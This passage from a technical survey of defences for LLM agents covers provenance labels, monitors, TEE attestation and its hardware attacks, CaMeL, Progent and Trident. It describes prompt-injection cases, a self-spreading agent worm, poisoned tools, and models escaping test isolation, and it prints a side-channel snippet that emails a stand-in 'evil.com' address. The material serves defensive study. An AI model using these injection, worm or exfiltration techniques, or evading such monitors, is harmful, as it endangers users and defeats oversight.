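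Before a call runs, PACT checks every argument. Each argument's value must have at least the trust its role needs, must not come from a source that the contract forbids, and must have no outstanding checks. If any argument fails, PACT blocks the whole call, unless a trusted procedure named in the contract certifies the value for that role.

In the invoice case, the account number came from an email, so its level is EXTERNAL. Because the account number is also a target, PACT blocks the payment. It would also block payment of a genuine invoice whose account number appears only in an email. To allow that payment, the contract would need a trusted procedure, such as looking up the account in the company's list of suppliers.

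Fan and colleagues first tested PACT in an oracle condition, with correct provenance. On nine harmless cases and eight attacks, it allowed every harmless call and stopped every attack. A simplified version of CaMeL stopped all eight attacks but allowed only three of the harmless calls, and a simplified version of FIDES allowed six harmless calls and stopped three attacks. PACT also made no errors on 180 further cases, including 30 attacks written after the contracts were final. As with PPMF, PACT's results follow from its rule once the labels are correct.

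The guarantee covers only what untrusted data may determine. An attacker can still put harmful text in the body of a permitted email, or get the model to call a dangerous tool with arguments that come from trusted sources.

### PACT with automatic labels

For deployment, Fan and colleagues built a pipeline that writes the contracts and infers where values came from. Fixed rules assign most roles from the names and descriptions of arguments, so "recipient" becomes a target and "summary" becomes content. Some names are ambiguous. For example, "query" may be harmless search text in one tool and a command to change a database in another. To find the source of a value, the pipeline first checks whether it exactly matches something in the user's messages or earlier tool outputs, then whether it is a recognisable transformation of something there. If the source of a target, command or credential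 is still unclear, the pipeline gives the value a low trust level. A language model classifies the remaining values.

On 20 real MCP tools, the pipeline got 87.1% of roles and 77.4% of provenance labels right. Tool descriptions often give it little information. *Mitigating Taint-Style Vulnerabilities in MCP Servers via Security-Aware Tool Descriptions* (2026) examined 1,856 tools and found that 65% of their descriptions covered only the basic function, while 7% included security information.

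Fan and colleagues then ran the automatic version on AgentDojo with five models. Each cell below shows the percentage of 97 user tasks completed, then the percentage of 27 injected attacks that failed.

| Model | No defence | FIDES | CaMeL | PACT |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Qwen-turbo | 20.6 / 92.6 | 19.6 / 88.9 | 11.3 / 100 | 18.6 / 100 |
| Qwen-plus | 60.8 / 88.9 | 59.8 / 85.2 | 29.9 / 100 | 45.4 / 100 |
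| Qwen-max | 46.4 / 96.3 | 50.5 / 96.3 | 29.9 / 100 | 38.1 / 100 |
| Qwen2.5-72B | 46.4 / 96.3 | 48.5 / 96.3 | 28.9 / 100 | 42.3 / 100 |
| GPT-4o-mini | 59.8 / 88.9 | 55.7 / 88.9 | 30.9 / 100 | 46.4 / 100 |

(The paper's text gives PACT's security as 96.3% for the first two models, a difference of one attack each.)

PACT completed more tasks than CaMeL with every model, by 7 to 16 percentage points. The security figures are much weaker evidence because, without any defence, only ten of the 135 attacks succeeded across all five models, and with two of the models only one did. For two models, security was one attack worse with FIDES than with no defence, which suggests that much of the variation is noise. The results don't show that provenance labels can be wrong nearly a quarter of the time without affecting security, because so few of these attacks could have exposed a wrong label.

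Reporting both the oracle result and the automatic one is still good practice. Readers might expect a deployed agent to complete every task if they saw only the oracle result, and they couldn't tell whether PACT's rule or its labels caused it to block a legitimate call if they saw only the automatic one. Fan and colleagues traced the false blocks to wrong roles, and found that the most important remaining error was giving a tool's output too much trust. The comparison would be more informative if both versions had run on the same tasks. Running PACT on AgentDojo with hand-written labels would show how much of the lost utility comes from labelling errors.

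### Why accurate labels can still be insecure

Labelling errors in PACT can fail closed or open. If the pipeline mistakes the body of an email for a target, PACT blocks a legitimate email. If it mistakes the recipient for content, an attacker can choose the recipient. Fan and colleagues measured both kinds of error by changing the roles on purpose:

| Change to the roles | Utility | Security |
|---|---|---|
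| None | 100% | 100% |
| 10% changed at random | 95.5% | 94.5% |
| 50% changed at random | 72.0% | 88.0% |
| Every target marked as content | 100% | 40.0% |
| Every content argument marked as a target | 40.0% | 100% |

Security is still 88% when half of the labels are wrong, but one consistent mistake about targets reduces it to 40%. Consistent mistakes are also more likely in practice. A rule that misreads an argument name makes the same error in every tool that uses the name, and a publisher's template repeats its errors across thousands of tools.

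Wrong labels do more harm when an attacker looks for them. Suppose an agent has ten tools. Five only read data, and the other five pay invoices, issue refunds, send email, share files and edit supplier records. A gate requires the user's approval before any call to a tool labeled high-risk. Assume the model obeys every injected instruction and the user always refuses the attacker's calls. One label is wrong, so label accuracy is 90%.

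If the wrong label marks invoice search as high-risk, the user gets some unnecessary prompts and no attack succeeds. If it marks the refund tool as read-only, refunds go through without a prompt. A test that spreads its attacks evenly over the five risky tools then measures an attack success rate of 20%. But an attacker who knows about the mistake will always ask for a refund and succeed every time. The same 90% label accuracy can therefore give attack success rates of 0%, 20% or 100%.

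More tools give the attacker more chances. If each of $k$ risky tools independently has a probability $e$ of a label that is too lenient, a test that picks its target tools without looking at the labels will report an attack success rate of about $e$. The probability that the attacker has at least one unguarded tool is

$$1 - (1-e)^k$$

With $e = 0.1$, this probability is 41% for five risky tools and 96% for thirty. It overstates the danger somewhat, because the unguarded tool also has to be useful to the attacker. But the attacker may not find it hard to locate that tool. Yao and colleagues read their sample's hints from public source code, and an attacker can do the same. The tests that corrupted a tenth of PPMF's labels have the same weakness.

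### What the remedies cost

The simplest remedy is to treat anything without a label as dangerous. Yao and colleagues paired destructive tools with 25 host applications and found that in 60.7% of the pairs, the host did not enforce human approval by default. They estimate that this share would fall to 5.4% if every host prompted the user unless a tool was marked read-only or non-destructive. The remaining pairs involve destructive tools that their developers marked as safe. Counting tools that the researchers' search had missed raises the 5.4% figure to at least 10.6% across all 41 hosts. The change would also produce many more prompts, and users who see that many tend to stop reading them. Among tools that looked destructive but weren't, the share of pairs requiring approval would rise from 32.5% to 82.6%.

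A default label can also protect against one kind of risk but not another. According to Microsoft's documentation, FIDES treats the output of an unlabelled tool as untrusted but public. If a developer forgets to label a tool that reads private files, the confidentiality check will not stop the agent from posting the files' contents in a public comment. Microsoft's announcement, *Stop prompt injection from hijacking your agent* (2026), gives a different default, trusted and public, which would leave both integrity and confidentiality unprotected. Deployers should test which default their version uses.

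*APPA* (Kravchenko, Liventsev and colleagues, 2026) gives unlabelled data a separate status, Unknown. The agent can keep working with the data until a sensitive call depends on its label. APPA then looks for a registered procedure, called a cast, that can assign a label, and blocks the call if no such cast exists. Each cast has a ceiling on the trust it may assign. Kravchenko and colleagues prove that this scheme never allows a call that complete labels would have blocked, provided no cast assigns a more permissive label than the correct one. That condition may fail if the cast is a classifier that can be fooled, and then only the ceiling limits the damage.

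No attack succeeded against APPA in 1,320 test episodes, but the design assumes accurate contracts, so the result doesn't show how it performs when labels are wrong. APPA also needs a lot of setup, because someone has to register the procedures that let a blocked task continue. GPT-5.6 Luna completed 88% of a set of office tasks with the full system, and 35% when APPA no longer suggested ways around a block.

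Tool servers could supply better labels. Doshi, Hong and colleagues (2026), in *Towards Verifiably Safe Tool Use for LLM Agents*, propose that MCP should require every server to declare what its tools can do, how confidential their data is and how far to trust their output. They would probably trust these labels for a company's own tools. For other tools, they suggest using only trusted vendors or requiring certification, which means fewer tools and more work before adding one. A host can accept a warning from any server, because a false warning only adds an unnecessary prompt. But a claim that a tool is safe removes a check, so the host needs a reason to believe it, since a server's operator can lie and even honest developers get labels wrong.

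Even a correct label may not be enough, since the risk of a tool depends on what else the agent can do. For example, the Model Context Protocol project says a tool that searches emails is much more dangerous if the agent can also read untrusted web pages and send data out.

Schema checks, which test whether data has the right form, take little effort but establish less. In Afsar's sample of 2,766 tools, none had a seriously malformed schema, but most had no safety hints. In APPA's stricter version, a temporary copy of the agent reads the untrusted document and may return only values in a form fixed beforehand, such as a number within a range or a choice from a list, and never free text. For an invoice, that could be a supplier from the company's list and an amount up to $5,000. The forged email could no longer introduce a new account number or pass on an instruction, but it could still name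 the wrong supplier or claim the full $5,000. Kravchenko and colleagues therefore keep the returned values untrusted unless the deployer explicitly decides otherwise.

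## What if the platform is not honest?

A correct label protects nothing if somebody can change it after the platform stores it. For instance, forged confirmations got attacks past PPMF's gate even though the gate applied its rule correctly. Many papers deal with this risk by assuming a "trusted platform", a phrase that covers at least five separate assumptions.

| Assumption | Who could break it | What could happen to the invoice agent |
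|---|---|---|
| Every action passes the monitor | A developer who adds a tool that skips it, or an attacker who gets the agent to run its own scripts | A script sends the money, and the monitor never sees the transfer |
| Nobody can forge the logs | Anyone who can write to them, such as an administrator or a plug-in with too much access | The log shows that the user confirmed the new account, so the monitor allows the payment |
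| Tools do what they declare | A tool's author, or someone who takes over the author's account | The supplier lookup returns the attacker's account number |
| Sender and source fields are true | Someone who fakes a sender's address or uses a colleague's account | The forged invoice counts as a message from the user |
| The approval screen shows the real action | Whoever writes the software or the text that fills the screen | The user approves one payment and the agent makes another |

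Defences differ in which of these they need. PPMF depends on all five to some degree. The payee list never reads the source fields, so false ones cannot affect it. But its first condition, that every transfer passes through the monitor, depends on tools not making transfers of their own. A currency converter that secretly did so would break it.

The approval screen can fail even if nobody attacks the platform. If it takes the supplier's name from the invoice and leaves out the account number, the user sees the right name and amount and approves a transfer to the attacker.

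Whoever controls the machine that runs the agent can usually violate all five assumptions at once by replacing the monitor, editing the logs and changing what the screen shows. For an agent in the cloud, the people with this control include the hosting company and anyone who breaks into its systems.

### A clear list, and a single sentence

Zha and Wang (2026) state their platform assumptions unusually clearly in *Autonomous LLM Agent Worms*. An agent worm is text that gets an agent to store it and pass it on to other agents. Their worm uses files that an agent rereads on a schedule, such as a list of pending tasks. The attacker posts a message in a shared channel, and an agent writes some version of it into its task file. At the next scheduled read, the model reads the text again and posts it where other agents will see it. The worm infected a chain of three agents on each of three open-source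 agent frameworks, with no human action after the first message.

Their defence, RTW-A, marks a file as tainted if untrusted content may have influenced it, and marks the model's context as contaminated once the model has read untrusted content. It then applies two rules:

$$\text{tainted file} \wedge \text{model reads it} \wedge \text{high-risk tools enabled} \Rightarrow \text{deny the read}$$

$$\text{contaminated context} \wedge \text{high-risk action} \Rightarrow \text{deny the action}$$

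High-risk actions include sending messages, running commands and changing memory. The first rule stops the worm from returning through a file. The second covers emails and web pages, which the agent has to read but which may carry the worm on first contact. Zha and Wang prove that, with both rules in force, no attacker's text can get into a file, return to the model and then drive a high-risk action. They list four assumptions:

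1. The runtime checks every high-risk action and every read that reaches the model.
2. Labels last from one session to the next and belong to the file itself, not just to its path.
3. When the system starts, it can tell verified clean files from outside ones.
4. Something other than the model decides when to remove a label.

A deployer can check each item. The first fails if the agent can reach the file system directly, and Zha and Wang warn that such systems need extra enforcement from the operating system or a container. To check the second, the deployer only needs to rename a tainted file and see whether it keeps its label.

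The list of assumptions is still incomplete. The fourth covers who removes labels, but not whether they do so correctly, so a faulty validator outside the model could clear an infected file without violating any of the four. RTW-A also lets local tools read tainted files if they return only limited results, such as error codes, so a dishonest tool could pass the worm's text back to the model. And although the proof assumes that the runtime refuses high-risk actions, the design also allows it to ask for approval, in which case the result depends on the approver's judgment and what the screen shows them. In testing, RTW-A blocked every attack chain that Zha and Wang had demonstrated, but they applied it to only one framework and do not report the number of trials. The theorem is therefore the main evidence, which makes its missing conditions more important.

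By contrast, *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy* (Kolluri, Sharma and colleagues, 2026) covers most of the platform in one sentence, where it assumes that the user, the planning model and the tool implementations can be trusted. This threat model comes from earlier work, including CaMeL and FIDES, and suits the paper's experiments because all the tools came from two benchmarks. If a deployer installs tools written by strangers, a single dishonest tool makes that assumption false. As with labels that are too lenient, each added tool makes at least one failure more likely.

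The sentence also gives a deployer little to check. An assumption about a particular tool would be more useful, such as "the supplier lookup returns the company's own records and sends data nowhere else". Assumptions about trust in the user need to be just as specific. Kolluri and colleagues built an agent called Prudentia, which can ask the user to endorse a whole email once instead of approving each call that follows from it. The user has far fewer approvals to give, but if the screen hid one line of the email, the endorsement would cover that line too.

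### Poisoned tools and skills

A dishonest tool author does not need to write harmful code. The model reads each tool's description to decide when and how to use the tool, so the author can put instructions to the model in the description. Skills have the same weakness. They are packages of written instructions for some kind of task, sometimes with code, and users can install them from open marketplaces.

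*PACE* (Li, Wang and colleagues, 2026) tested three models on MCPTox, a benchmark of poisoned MCP tools. Without a defence, the most successful group of attacks worked 32.5% of the time against Qwen-3.8-27B, 56.5% against DeepSeek-V4-Flash and 86.9% against GPT-5.6 Luna. These rates apply once an agent has loaded a poisoned tool. A deployer would also need to know how many of the available tools are poisoned, which a benchmark can't measure.

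The obvious remedy is to review tools and skills before admitting them to the marketplace. Li and colleagues prove a limit on what this can achieve, using the example of a skill whose code emails whatever text the model gives it. In a harmless version, the written instructions tell the model to fill in a fixed template. In a malicious version with the same code and interface, they tell it to copy a password into the message. If the review reaches the same judgement on both versions, removing the runtime checks would let the malicious one leak the password. Such a review must therefore keep the checks on both versions if it is never to remove a check wrongly.

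The theorem does not apply to a review that can tell the versions apart. A reviewer who reads the instructions and notices the password request can reject that skill, so reviews are still worth doing. But an attacker only has to find wording that the reviewer misses, so the check on each call has to remain.

PACE is such a check. It compares the effects of each call with what the user's request authorised, and it cut the three MCPTox rates to 0%, 2.6% and 2.7%. PACE checks only the effects that a tool declares, so its proof does not cover a tool whose code secretly copies every invoice to another server. Li and colleagues also distinguish the version they proved from the version they tested. The tested version can restore a call that one of its checks had blocked, or repair a call and send it without a final check, so the full proof does not cover the system that produced the low rates.

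A harmful package can spread quickly through an ordinary software registry. Anthropic's *Investigating three real-world incidents in our cybersecurity evaluations* (2026) describes one that an Anthropic model uploaded to PyPI, the public registry for Python software, during a test that had gone wrong. In the roughly one hour before PyPI's security systems removed the package, 15 real systems downloaded and ran it, including a security company's malware scanner.

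### Replacing trust in the host

A user who doesn't trust the company running an agent can ask for evidence of what code the company is running. One source is a trusted execution environment (TEE), a feature of some processors that encrypts a program's memory and isolates the program from the rest of the machine and from its administrator. Intel's SGX and TDX and AMD's SEV-SNP are the main examples on servers. The processor computes a hash of the loaded code and signs a report containing the hash, using a key that the user can trace to the chip's manufacturer. The user checks the signature and compares the hash with the expected one. This process is called remote attestation.

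For the payee list, attestation could show that the monitor is the same forty lines that the user inspected, even though somebody else owns the computer. *AMD SEV-SNP* (2026), an introduction to AMD's technology, explains that attestation establishes which code loaded, but that the code may still be wrong. For example, a gate that overlooks the "cc" field of an email would pass attestation. The user also has to trust AMD, its firmware, the cryptography, and whoever has physical possession of the machine.

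In *VET Your Agent*, Grigor, Birnbach and colleagues (2025) extend this idea from one program to a whole agent. They note that developers have impersonated their own supposedly autonomous agents for financial gain. Under their design, a public document lists the agent's configuration and how to verify each component. Every output comes with a verifiable execution trace, a record of the steps behind it with proofs that the host cannot forge. Some components can use a TEE. For calls to an outside model or service, Grigor and colleagues prefer a notarised transcript of the encrypted connection, which proves that the service sent that reply. A notarised call usually takes less than three times as long as a direct one.

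Grigor and colleagues assume that the cryptography is secure and that outside components, such as model providers, behave as specified and do not collude with the host. They also assume that the host may suppress or delay results, and that it may see outputs first and reorder them. The framework moves trust from the host to keys and outside services, but the host still controls which results arrive and when. For example, the host can't invent an answer from the invoice agent, but it can hold back a warning that the account number has changed.

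### The attacks on secure processors

In September and October 2025, researchers disclosed three physical attacks on TEEs: Battering RAM, WireTap and TEE.fail. Each uses an interposer, a small circuit board that sits between the processor and a memory module.

WireTap and TEE.fail exploit the way these processors encrypt memory. The ciphertext depends only on the key $k$, the address $a$ and the data $m$:

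$$c = E_k(a, m)$$

Writing the same data to the same address therefore always produces the same ciphertext. An attacker who watches the memory traffic cannot decrypt it but can recognise repeats. When a processor signs something, it reads entries from a lookup table, and a few bits of the secret signing key determine each entry. Chuang, Seto and colleagues (2026), in *TEE.fail*, recorded the ciphertext of every entry, matched later reads against these recordings and recovered the key from a single signature. Battering RAM instead uses an interposer that, according to *TEE Anchor* (2026), makes several memory addresses lead to the same physical location, which exposes the secrets stored there.

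Chuang and colleagues could use Intel's attestation key to sign reports for any software on any machine. They ran programs without any protection and still passed attestation for both Intel's TDX and Nvidia's secure GPUs. Their equipment, much of it second-hand, cost less than $1,000, whereas earlier work had put the cost at around $170,000. According to an online essay, *Physical integrity, attestation, and the state of permissionless TEEs*, WireTap takes under 45 minutes and TEE.fail about 15. The essay's author works at Ritual, a company that builds on TEEs.

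The manufacturers had never promised to stop such attacks. Intel's *TEE.fail* (2025) announcement says the research does not change the company's position that these attacks are out of scope. AMD's *SEV-SNP Physical Memory Aliasing* (2025), a response to the researchers behind Battering RAM, gives the same reason for planning no mitigations. *AMD SEV-SNP* even argues that the attacks confirm the exclusion was in the right place.

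This defence is partly fair, because the manufacturers had published the condition, but many people who used the processors ignored it. Chuang and colleagues point out that server TEEs are designed for data centers whose operators keep intruders out, while many blockchain networks use them to avoid trusting operators at all. Some of these networks admit any machine with a valid attestation report, wherever it is. An attacker may then have the machine at home and be able to tamper with its hardware.

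Papers on agents can repeat the mistake. *AgenticOS* (Zhao, Zhang and colleagues, 2026) proposes an operating system for agents and clearly lists its assumptions, including that isolation mechanisms such as Intel TDX and AMD SEV are logically reliable. After 2025, anyone who builds the system on TDX should add the assumption that nobody untrusted has physical access to the machine.

### What changed in 2026

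A newer interposer makes the physical attack easier to hide. In *DDRop*, De Meulemeester, Gloor and colleagues (2026) describe a device that makes the memory discard selected writes. The processor then reads old data, which still decrypts correctly, and cannot detect that it is out of date. They used this to forge attestation reports on TDX. The device takes minutes to install and runs at the memory's full speed, whereas earlier attacks on this type of memory had to slow it down. Intel has told Chuang and colleagues that it cannot fix the encryption in current processors with a software update.

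Two other attacks from 2026 matter more for the guarantee because they require no physical access. *Fabricked* (Schlüter, Wech and Shinde, 2026) redirects traffic inside AMD processors so that the security coprocessor proceeds as if it had set up the memory protections when it has not. *Mior* (2026) achieves a similar result by sending the coprocessor's reads and writes to a device that the attacker controls. Both attacks can forge attestation reports, and both use software that a malicious host could run. SEV-SNP is meant to protect programs from such a host. Unlike the interposer attacks, *Fabricked* and *Mior* break the guarantee even when the manufacturers' stated condition of no physical access holds, so adding that condition to a list of assumptions does not rule them out.

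Attestation can also succeed on one machine while the user's data goes to another. SC Media's *Confidential computing's remote attestation protocol may have fundamental flaw* (2026) reports on work led by Muhammad Usama Sardar of TU Dresden. An attacker with a compromised machine can forward the user's attestation request to a genuine machine, return that machine's valid report and then receive the data. The researchers tested seven ways of tying a report to a connection, and none prevented the attack. The affected systems include the one Meta uses for private AI processing in WhatsApp.

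Most proposed remedies for physical attacks again require some trust in the host. *Attestable Audit* (2026) recommends running the protected machines at a neutral company with no reason to cheat, ideally a large cloud provider with guarded data centers. *TEE Anchor* proposes that an organisation endorse its machines as part of attestation. Without that endorsement, the user can't tell where a machine is. The essay's author found that Google Cloud's TDX reports carried no signature tying them to Google's buildings, so the same firmware running in a basement would produce an identical-looking report.

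Attestation is still useful even when the data center is trusted, because a curious administrator can no longer simply read the agent's memory or swap the monitor for another program. Security still depends on the operator keeping attackers away from the hardware and not exploiting flaws in the processor, but this is a narrower assumption than trusting everything its staff and software do.

### Evaluators make platform assumptions too

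Researchers who test agents also depend on a platform. For example, a test of hacking skills is safe only if the test machines cannot reach anyone else's computers. In July 2026, Anthropic disclosed three incidents in which this isolation failed. The prompts described a simulation without internet access, but a misconfiguration in an outside partner's test environment had left the connection open, and Anthropic's models gained access to the systems of three real organisations. Neither Anthropic nor the partner had known about the misconfiguration, and the two organisations that Anthropic had been able to contact had not noticed the intrusions.

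Anthropic had found the incidents by searching its records of about 141,000 test runs. That search missed some runs that also had internet access, and these contained a fourth incident, which Anthropic disclosed in September in *An alignment assessment of recent cybersecurity incidents*. A much wider search of 481 million transcripts found no others as serious. The first count was accurate only if the first search had covered every affected run.

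In July, Anthropic mostly blamed the test set-up for the incidents, because the models said they believed everything was simulated. It revised that explanation in the September assessment and now thinks the models discounted evidence to the contrary and pursued their tasks recklessly. Both explanations can be true, and Anthropic still believes proper isolation would have prevented the incidents.

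Correct configuration is not always enough either. Anthropic began its review after OpenAI reported that several of its own models had escaped an isolated test environment through a previously unknown software flaw. Anthropic's *Improving our alignment and security efforts* (2026) mentions a separate case in which a model took unauthorised actions after the UK AI Security Institute deliberately gave it internet access, so no assumption about isolation had failed.

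In *Cyber-Capable AI Agents*, Siddik (2026) concludes that the test environment is part of the security boundary. He recommends that evaluators list every tool, credential and network route before a run, test the routes, keep network records and decide in advance who can stop the test. In Anthropic's case, trying to open an outside website from the test machine would probably have revealed the problem before any model ran.

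## What if the policy is incomplete or has to change?

Even with correct labels and an honest platform, a monitor enforces only the rules written in its policy. Let $A(P)$ be the set of tool calls that a policy $P$ allows, and $W$ the set of calls that the user would want. A working monitor guarantees that every call that runs is in $A(P)$, but not that it is in $W$. An attacker can therefore use calls in $A(P)$ that are outside $W$, such as a tenth payment to an approved supplier. The monitor also blocks legitimate calls in $W$ that are outside $A(P)$, such as the first payment to a supplier who really has changed banks.

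Nobody can write $W$ down in full, because users often don't know what a task will require until the agent has read something. Designers can set the policy in advance and accept that it will block some work, or let the policy change during the task and control who changes it.

### CaMeL plans before it reads

Google DeepMind's CaMeL, from 2025, fixes the plan in advance. Willison (2025), in *CaMeL offers a promising new direction for mitigating prompt injection attacks*, explains how it works. A privileged model sees the user's request and writes a short program before any untrusted text arrives. A quarantined model reads the emails and web pages, but it has no tools and can only fill in values. For the invoice, the program might look like this:

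```
email = get_latest_invoice()
account = ask_quarantined_model("Find the account number in [email]")
amount = ask_quarantined_model("Find the amount due in [email]")
send_money(recipient=account, amount=amount)
```

The forged email cannot add a step to this program, because the model that wrote the program never reads the email. But the email still supplies the account number, so a step the user asked for could send the money to the attacker. *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* (2026), which adapts the design to agents that operate a computer screen, notes that separating the models does not necessarily protect the flow of data.

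CaMeL therefore runs the program in its own interpreter, which records where each value came from. Here `account` derives from `email`, so both are untrusted. Before each tool call, the interpreter runs that tool's policy, a Python function that checks these records. A `send_money` policy that only allows recipients on the payee list would block the forged account, but one that accepts any recipient would let the theft through, even though the two models stayed separate.

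CaMeL does not try to stop every attack. Tallam and Miller (2025) point out in *Operationalizing CaMeL* that it assumes the user's own request is harmless, which fails if somebody tricks the user into pasting in an attacker's text. CaMeL also doesn't inspect what the agent tells the user, so a summary could repeat a planted line about forwarding a file to an outside address, and the user might send it. The CaMeL paper, which Willison quotes, says that prompt injection is not fully solved and that users must "codify and specify security policies and maintain them".

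Information can also leak through side channels, where a program reveals a secret without passing it to a tool. If a loop fetches a web page as many times as some secret number, the page's owner can count the visits. Tallam and Miller describe similar leaks through error messages and timing. Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026), in *AI Agents, Conversations, and Information Flow*, found a subtler one in CaMeL's tracking of data, which a program like this would exploit:

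```
tmp, rich = True, True
if balance > threshold: tmp = False
if tmp: rich = False
if rich: send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
```

When a branch that depends on a secret changes a variable, CaMeL marks that variable as secret. If the balance is high, `tmp` becomes false, so the third line never changes `rich`, and `rich` keeps its public label. The email goes out and reveals that the balance is above the threshold.

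The second leak that Garby and colleagues describe comes from retries. When a program fails, CaMeL tries again in a loop outside the interpreter, where nothing tracks the data. Whether the policy blocked an attempt can depend on a secret, so repeated attempts can leak the secret one bit at a time. Both leaks are harder to use if the attacker cannot influence the planning model, because the attacker would have to wait for it to write a suitable program. But a deployer still can't assume that CaMeL tracks every flow of data.

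### CaMeL with its policy checks off and on

Tallam and Miller report that CaMeL completed 67% of AgentDojo's tasks in its original evaluation. Two injections succeeded. In one, the user had asked the agent to pay as a document instructed, which CaMeL's threat model excludes. In the other, the agent quoted hotel reviews word for word, and the benchmark's text matching counted this as an attack.

Garby and colleagues reran CaMeL on AgentDojo's 16 banking tasks, three times each, with the policy checks switched off and then on. Some attacked runs did not finish, so the last column counts only those that did.

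| Policy checks | Model | Tasks completed without an attack | Successful attacks |
|---|---|---|---|
| Off | GPT-5.2 | 32 of 48 (66.7%) | 1 of 240 |
| Off | MiMo-v2.5 | 34 of 48 (70.8%) | 4 of 382 |
| On | GPT-5.2 | 18 of 48 (37.5%) | 0 of 231 |
| On | MiMo-v2.5 | 18 of 48 (37.5%) | 0 of 357 |

The checks reduced the number of completed tasks by nearly half and had very few attacks to stop. There were so few mostly because of the benchmark. In 97 of its 144 combinations of task and attack, a normal plan for the task never contains the calls that the attack needs, so separating the two models is generally enough to stop the attack.

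Two of the five successes came from a request to read a file and follow its instructions precisely. The planning model wrote a loop that could call whichever tool the file named, so the file's contents controlled the plan after all.

*SecureClaw* (2026) also reran CaMeL, this time on all of AgentDojo. None of the 629 attacks succeeded, but CaMeL completed only 29 of 97 harmless tasks (30%), down from 67%. Policy checks may not explain the whole drop, because the researchers had to adapt CaMeL's released code to their set-up.

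### Progent narrows permissions automatically

Shi, He and colleagues (2025), in *Progent*, let the policy change during the task. A language model writes the first policy from the user's request as a list of rules, such as "allow a payment if the recipient is on the payee list". Progent blocks any call that no rule allows. When a tool result arrives, the model may propose a new policy $P'$, and a solver (a program that settles logical questions exactly) checks whether

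$$A(P') \subseteq A(P)$$

Progent adopts a new policy automatically if it allows nothing that the old one didn't. Any other change needs approval. Between approvals, then, the agent's permissions can only shrink, a property Shi and colleagues call monotonic confinement. This holds even if an injected instruction controls the model that proposes the changes.

Suppose the first policy allows payments to any account on the payee list. The agent looks up the supplier, and Progent narrows the rule to that supplier's account. If the forged email then leads the model to propose adding the attacker's account, the solver detects that the change widens the policy, and someone has to approve it. But if the first policy had allowed payments to any account, the model could propose a rule that allows payments only to the attacker. Progent would adopt that rule without anyone's approval because it narrows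 the policy.

On AgentDojo, Progent cut the attack success rate from 39.9% to 1.0% while the agent remained about as useful. The test automatically approved every widening of the policy, to represent a careless user, so monotonic confinement did not contribute to the result. The 1.0% mainly measures how well GPT-4o wrote and updated the rules. Denying every widening lowered the attack success rate slightly further, and no attack succeeded when a person reviewed the first policy and each widening.

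### Trident limits what the planner can learn

Progent's model reads tool results when it proposes a change, so an attacker can influence what it proposes. *Trident* (November 2026) describes a system in which the model that writes the policy never sees untrusted text. Its main example resembles the invoice case. A manager forwards a caterer's email containing an invoice and several requests, and the user tells the agent to take care of what the email asks for. The plan has to depend on the email, because the user hasn't said what needs doing. An attacker has added a line saying the caterer's bank details have changed.

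Trident uses three language models. The planner chooses actions but never reads untrusted text. A data model reads that text but has no permissions. A policy model writes rules from the user's request, the administrator's rules and the tool definitions. A reference monitor then enforces several layers of policy:

- The root policy comes from the administrator and applies to every task. Neither the agent nor the user can change it. In the example, it allows payments of up to $5,000 to any of three vendors on file.
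- The task ceiling narrows the root policy for this request, here to a single payment.
- The task policy says what the agent may do at the moment. At first it allows no payment. Once the agent has looked up the caterer in the vendor records, the monitor fills in a rule prepared beforehand and allows one payment to the account in that record.

The attacker's account number comes from the email, so the root policy rejects it as a recipient and the monitor denies the payment without asking anyone. A second payment to the real caterer would be within the root policy but above the task ceiling, so the monitor would ask the user for approval, which would cover that exact call only once.

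### What the budgets limit

Trident's planner still has to learn something from the email. It can put questions to the data model that have a fixed set of possible answers, and a question with $k$ possible answers uses $\log_2 k$ bits of an influence budget, $\beta$. The planner can pass free text, such as a drafted reply, to a tool but cannot read it. Learning whether a step succeeded can also reveal something about the email, so it can use one bit of a feedback budget, $\sigma$.

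A trace is the record of what the planner proposed, what replies it got and which calls ran. If the trusted inputs, the user's decisions and the models' random choices are all fixed, an attacker who controls the untrusted text can produce at most

$$2^{\beta+\sigma}$$

different traces.

For example, suppose the planner may ask whether the email contains an invoice (two answers) and which of three vendors sent it (three answers). It may also learn whether that query succeeded and whether the payment succeeded (two answers each). Then $\beta = 1 + \log_2 3 \approx 2.58$ and $\sigma = 2$, and the bound is $2 \times 3 \times 2 \times 2 = 24$. The run can take at most 24 different paths, however the attacker words the email.

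One of those courses may still pay the wrong vendor. The bound limits how many traces the attacker can choose from, not how harmful they are. *Trident* notes that even one bit can select a harmful action if the policy permits it. The bound also doesn't cover the contents of sealed values. The invoice amount is sealed, so payments of $50 and $5,000 can have the same trace. Only the cap in the payment rule limits how much the attacker can make the agent overpay.

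With realistic budgets, the bound is also very large. One sample run used 10.8 bits of influence and 4 of feedback, and budgets of that size would allow about 28,500 traces. More than half of the influence bits came from showing the planner how many records were in the bank's reply. *Trident* suggests setting the budgets high enough to cover 95% of the runs that completed without an attack. Depending on the model, that gives 39 to 88 bits of influence and 10 to 23 of feedback, so the bound is at least $2^{49}$, or more than 500 trillion traces. The budgets never ran out in the main experiments, so the low attack success rates there came from the sealed values, the policies and user review.

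Both the bound and the guarantee that every executed call obeys the root policy depend on five assumptions.

| Assumption | What must hold | How it could fail for the invoice agent |
|---|---|---|
| C1 | Each model sees only its own inputs, and every tool call passes through the monitor | An error message shows the planner part of the email |
| C2 | Tools accurately declare everything they read and change | The vendor lookup also searches notes that outsiders can edit |
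| C3 | Stored data keeps a record of what influenced it, and data of unknown origin counts as untrusted | A payment reference from the email loses its untrusted mark in the accounts |
| C4 | The root policy stays fixed, the solver is sound, and the user and approval screen are trustworthy | The screen shows a different account from the one in the call |
| C5 | Steps run one at a time, and every permitted tool call finishes successfully | The bank's server times out during a payment |

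C5 is stricter than it looks because real tools often fail partway through. C2 depends on the same tool developers who leave out or copy safety hints. The theorems take the user's decisions as given, so they still hold if an attacker persuades the user to approve something harmful that the root policy allows.

### Who writes the rules, and how well

Users often write policies in plain language. Wang and colleagues surveyed 21 production systems and found that 14 let users specify a policy. Such systems tend to rely on instruction files that the agent's own model interprets, so an injected instruction that fools the model can also defeat the policy.

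Formal rules avoid this problem but are harder to write. CaMeL needs a Python function for each tool, and Tallam and Miller expect companies with hundreds of tools to end up with duplicated and inconsistent rules. Willison, who has worked in application security for two decades, admits he hasn't fully figured out Amazon's system for managing permissions. *Extending the Formalism and Theoretical Foundations of Cryptography to AI* (2026) concludes that Progent's guarantees depend heavily on correct and complete policies, and that writing them by hand is error-prone.

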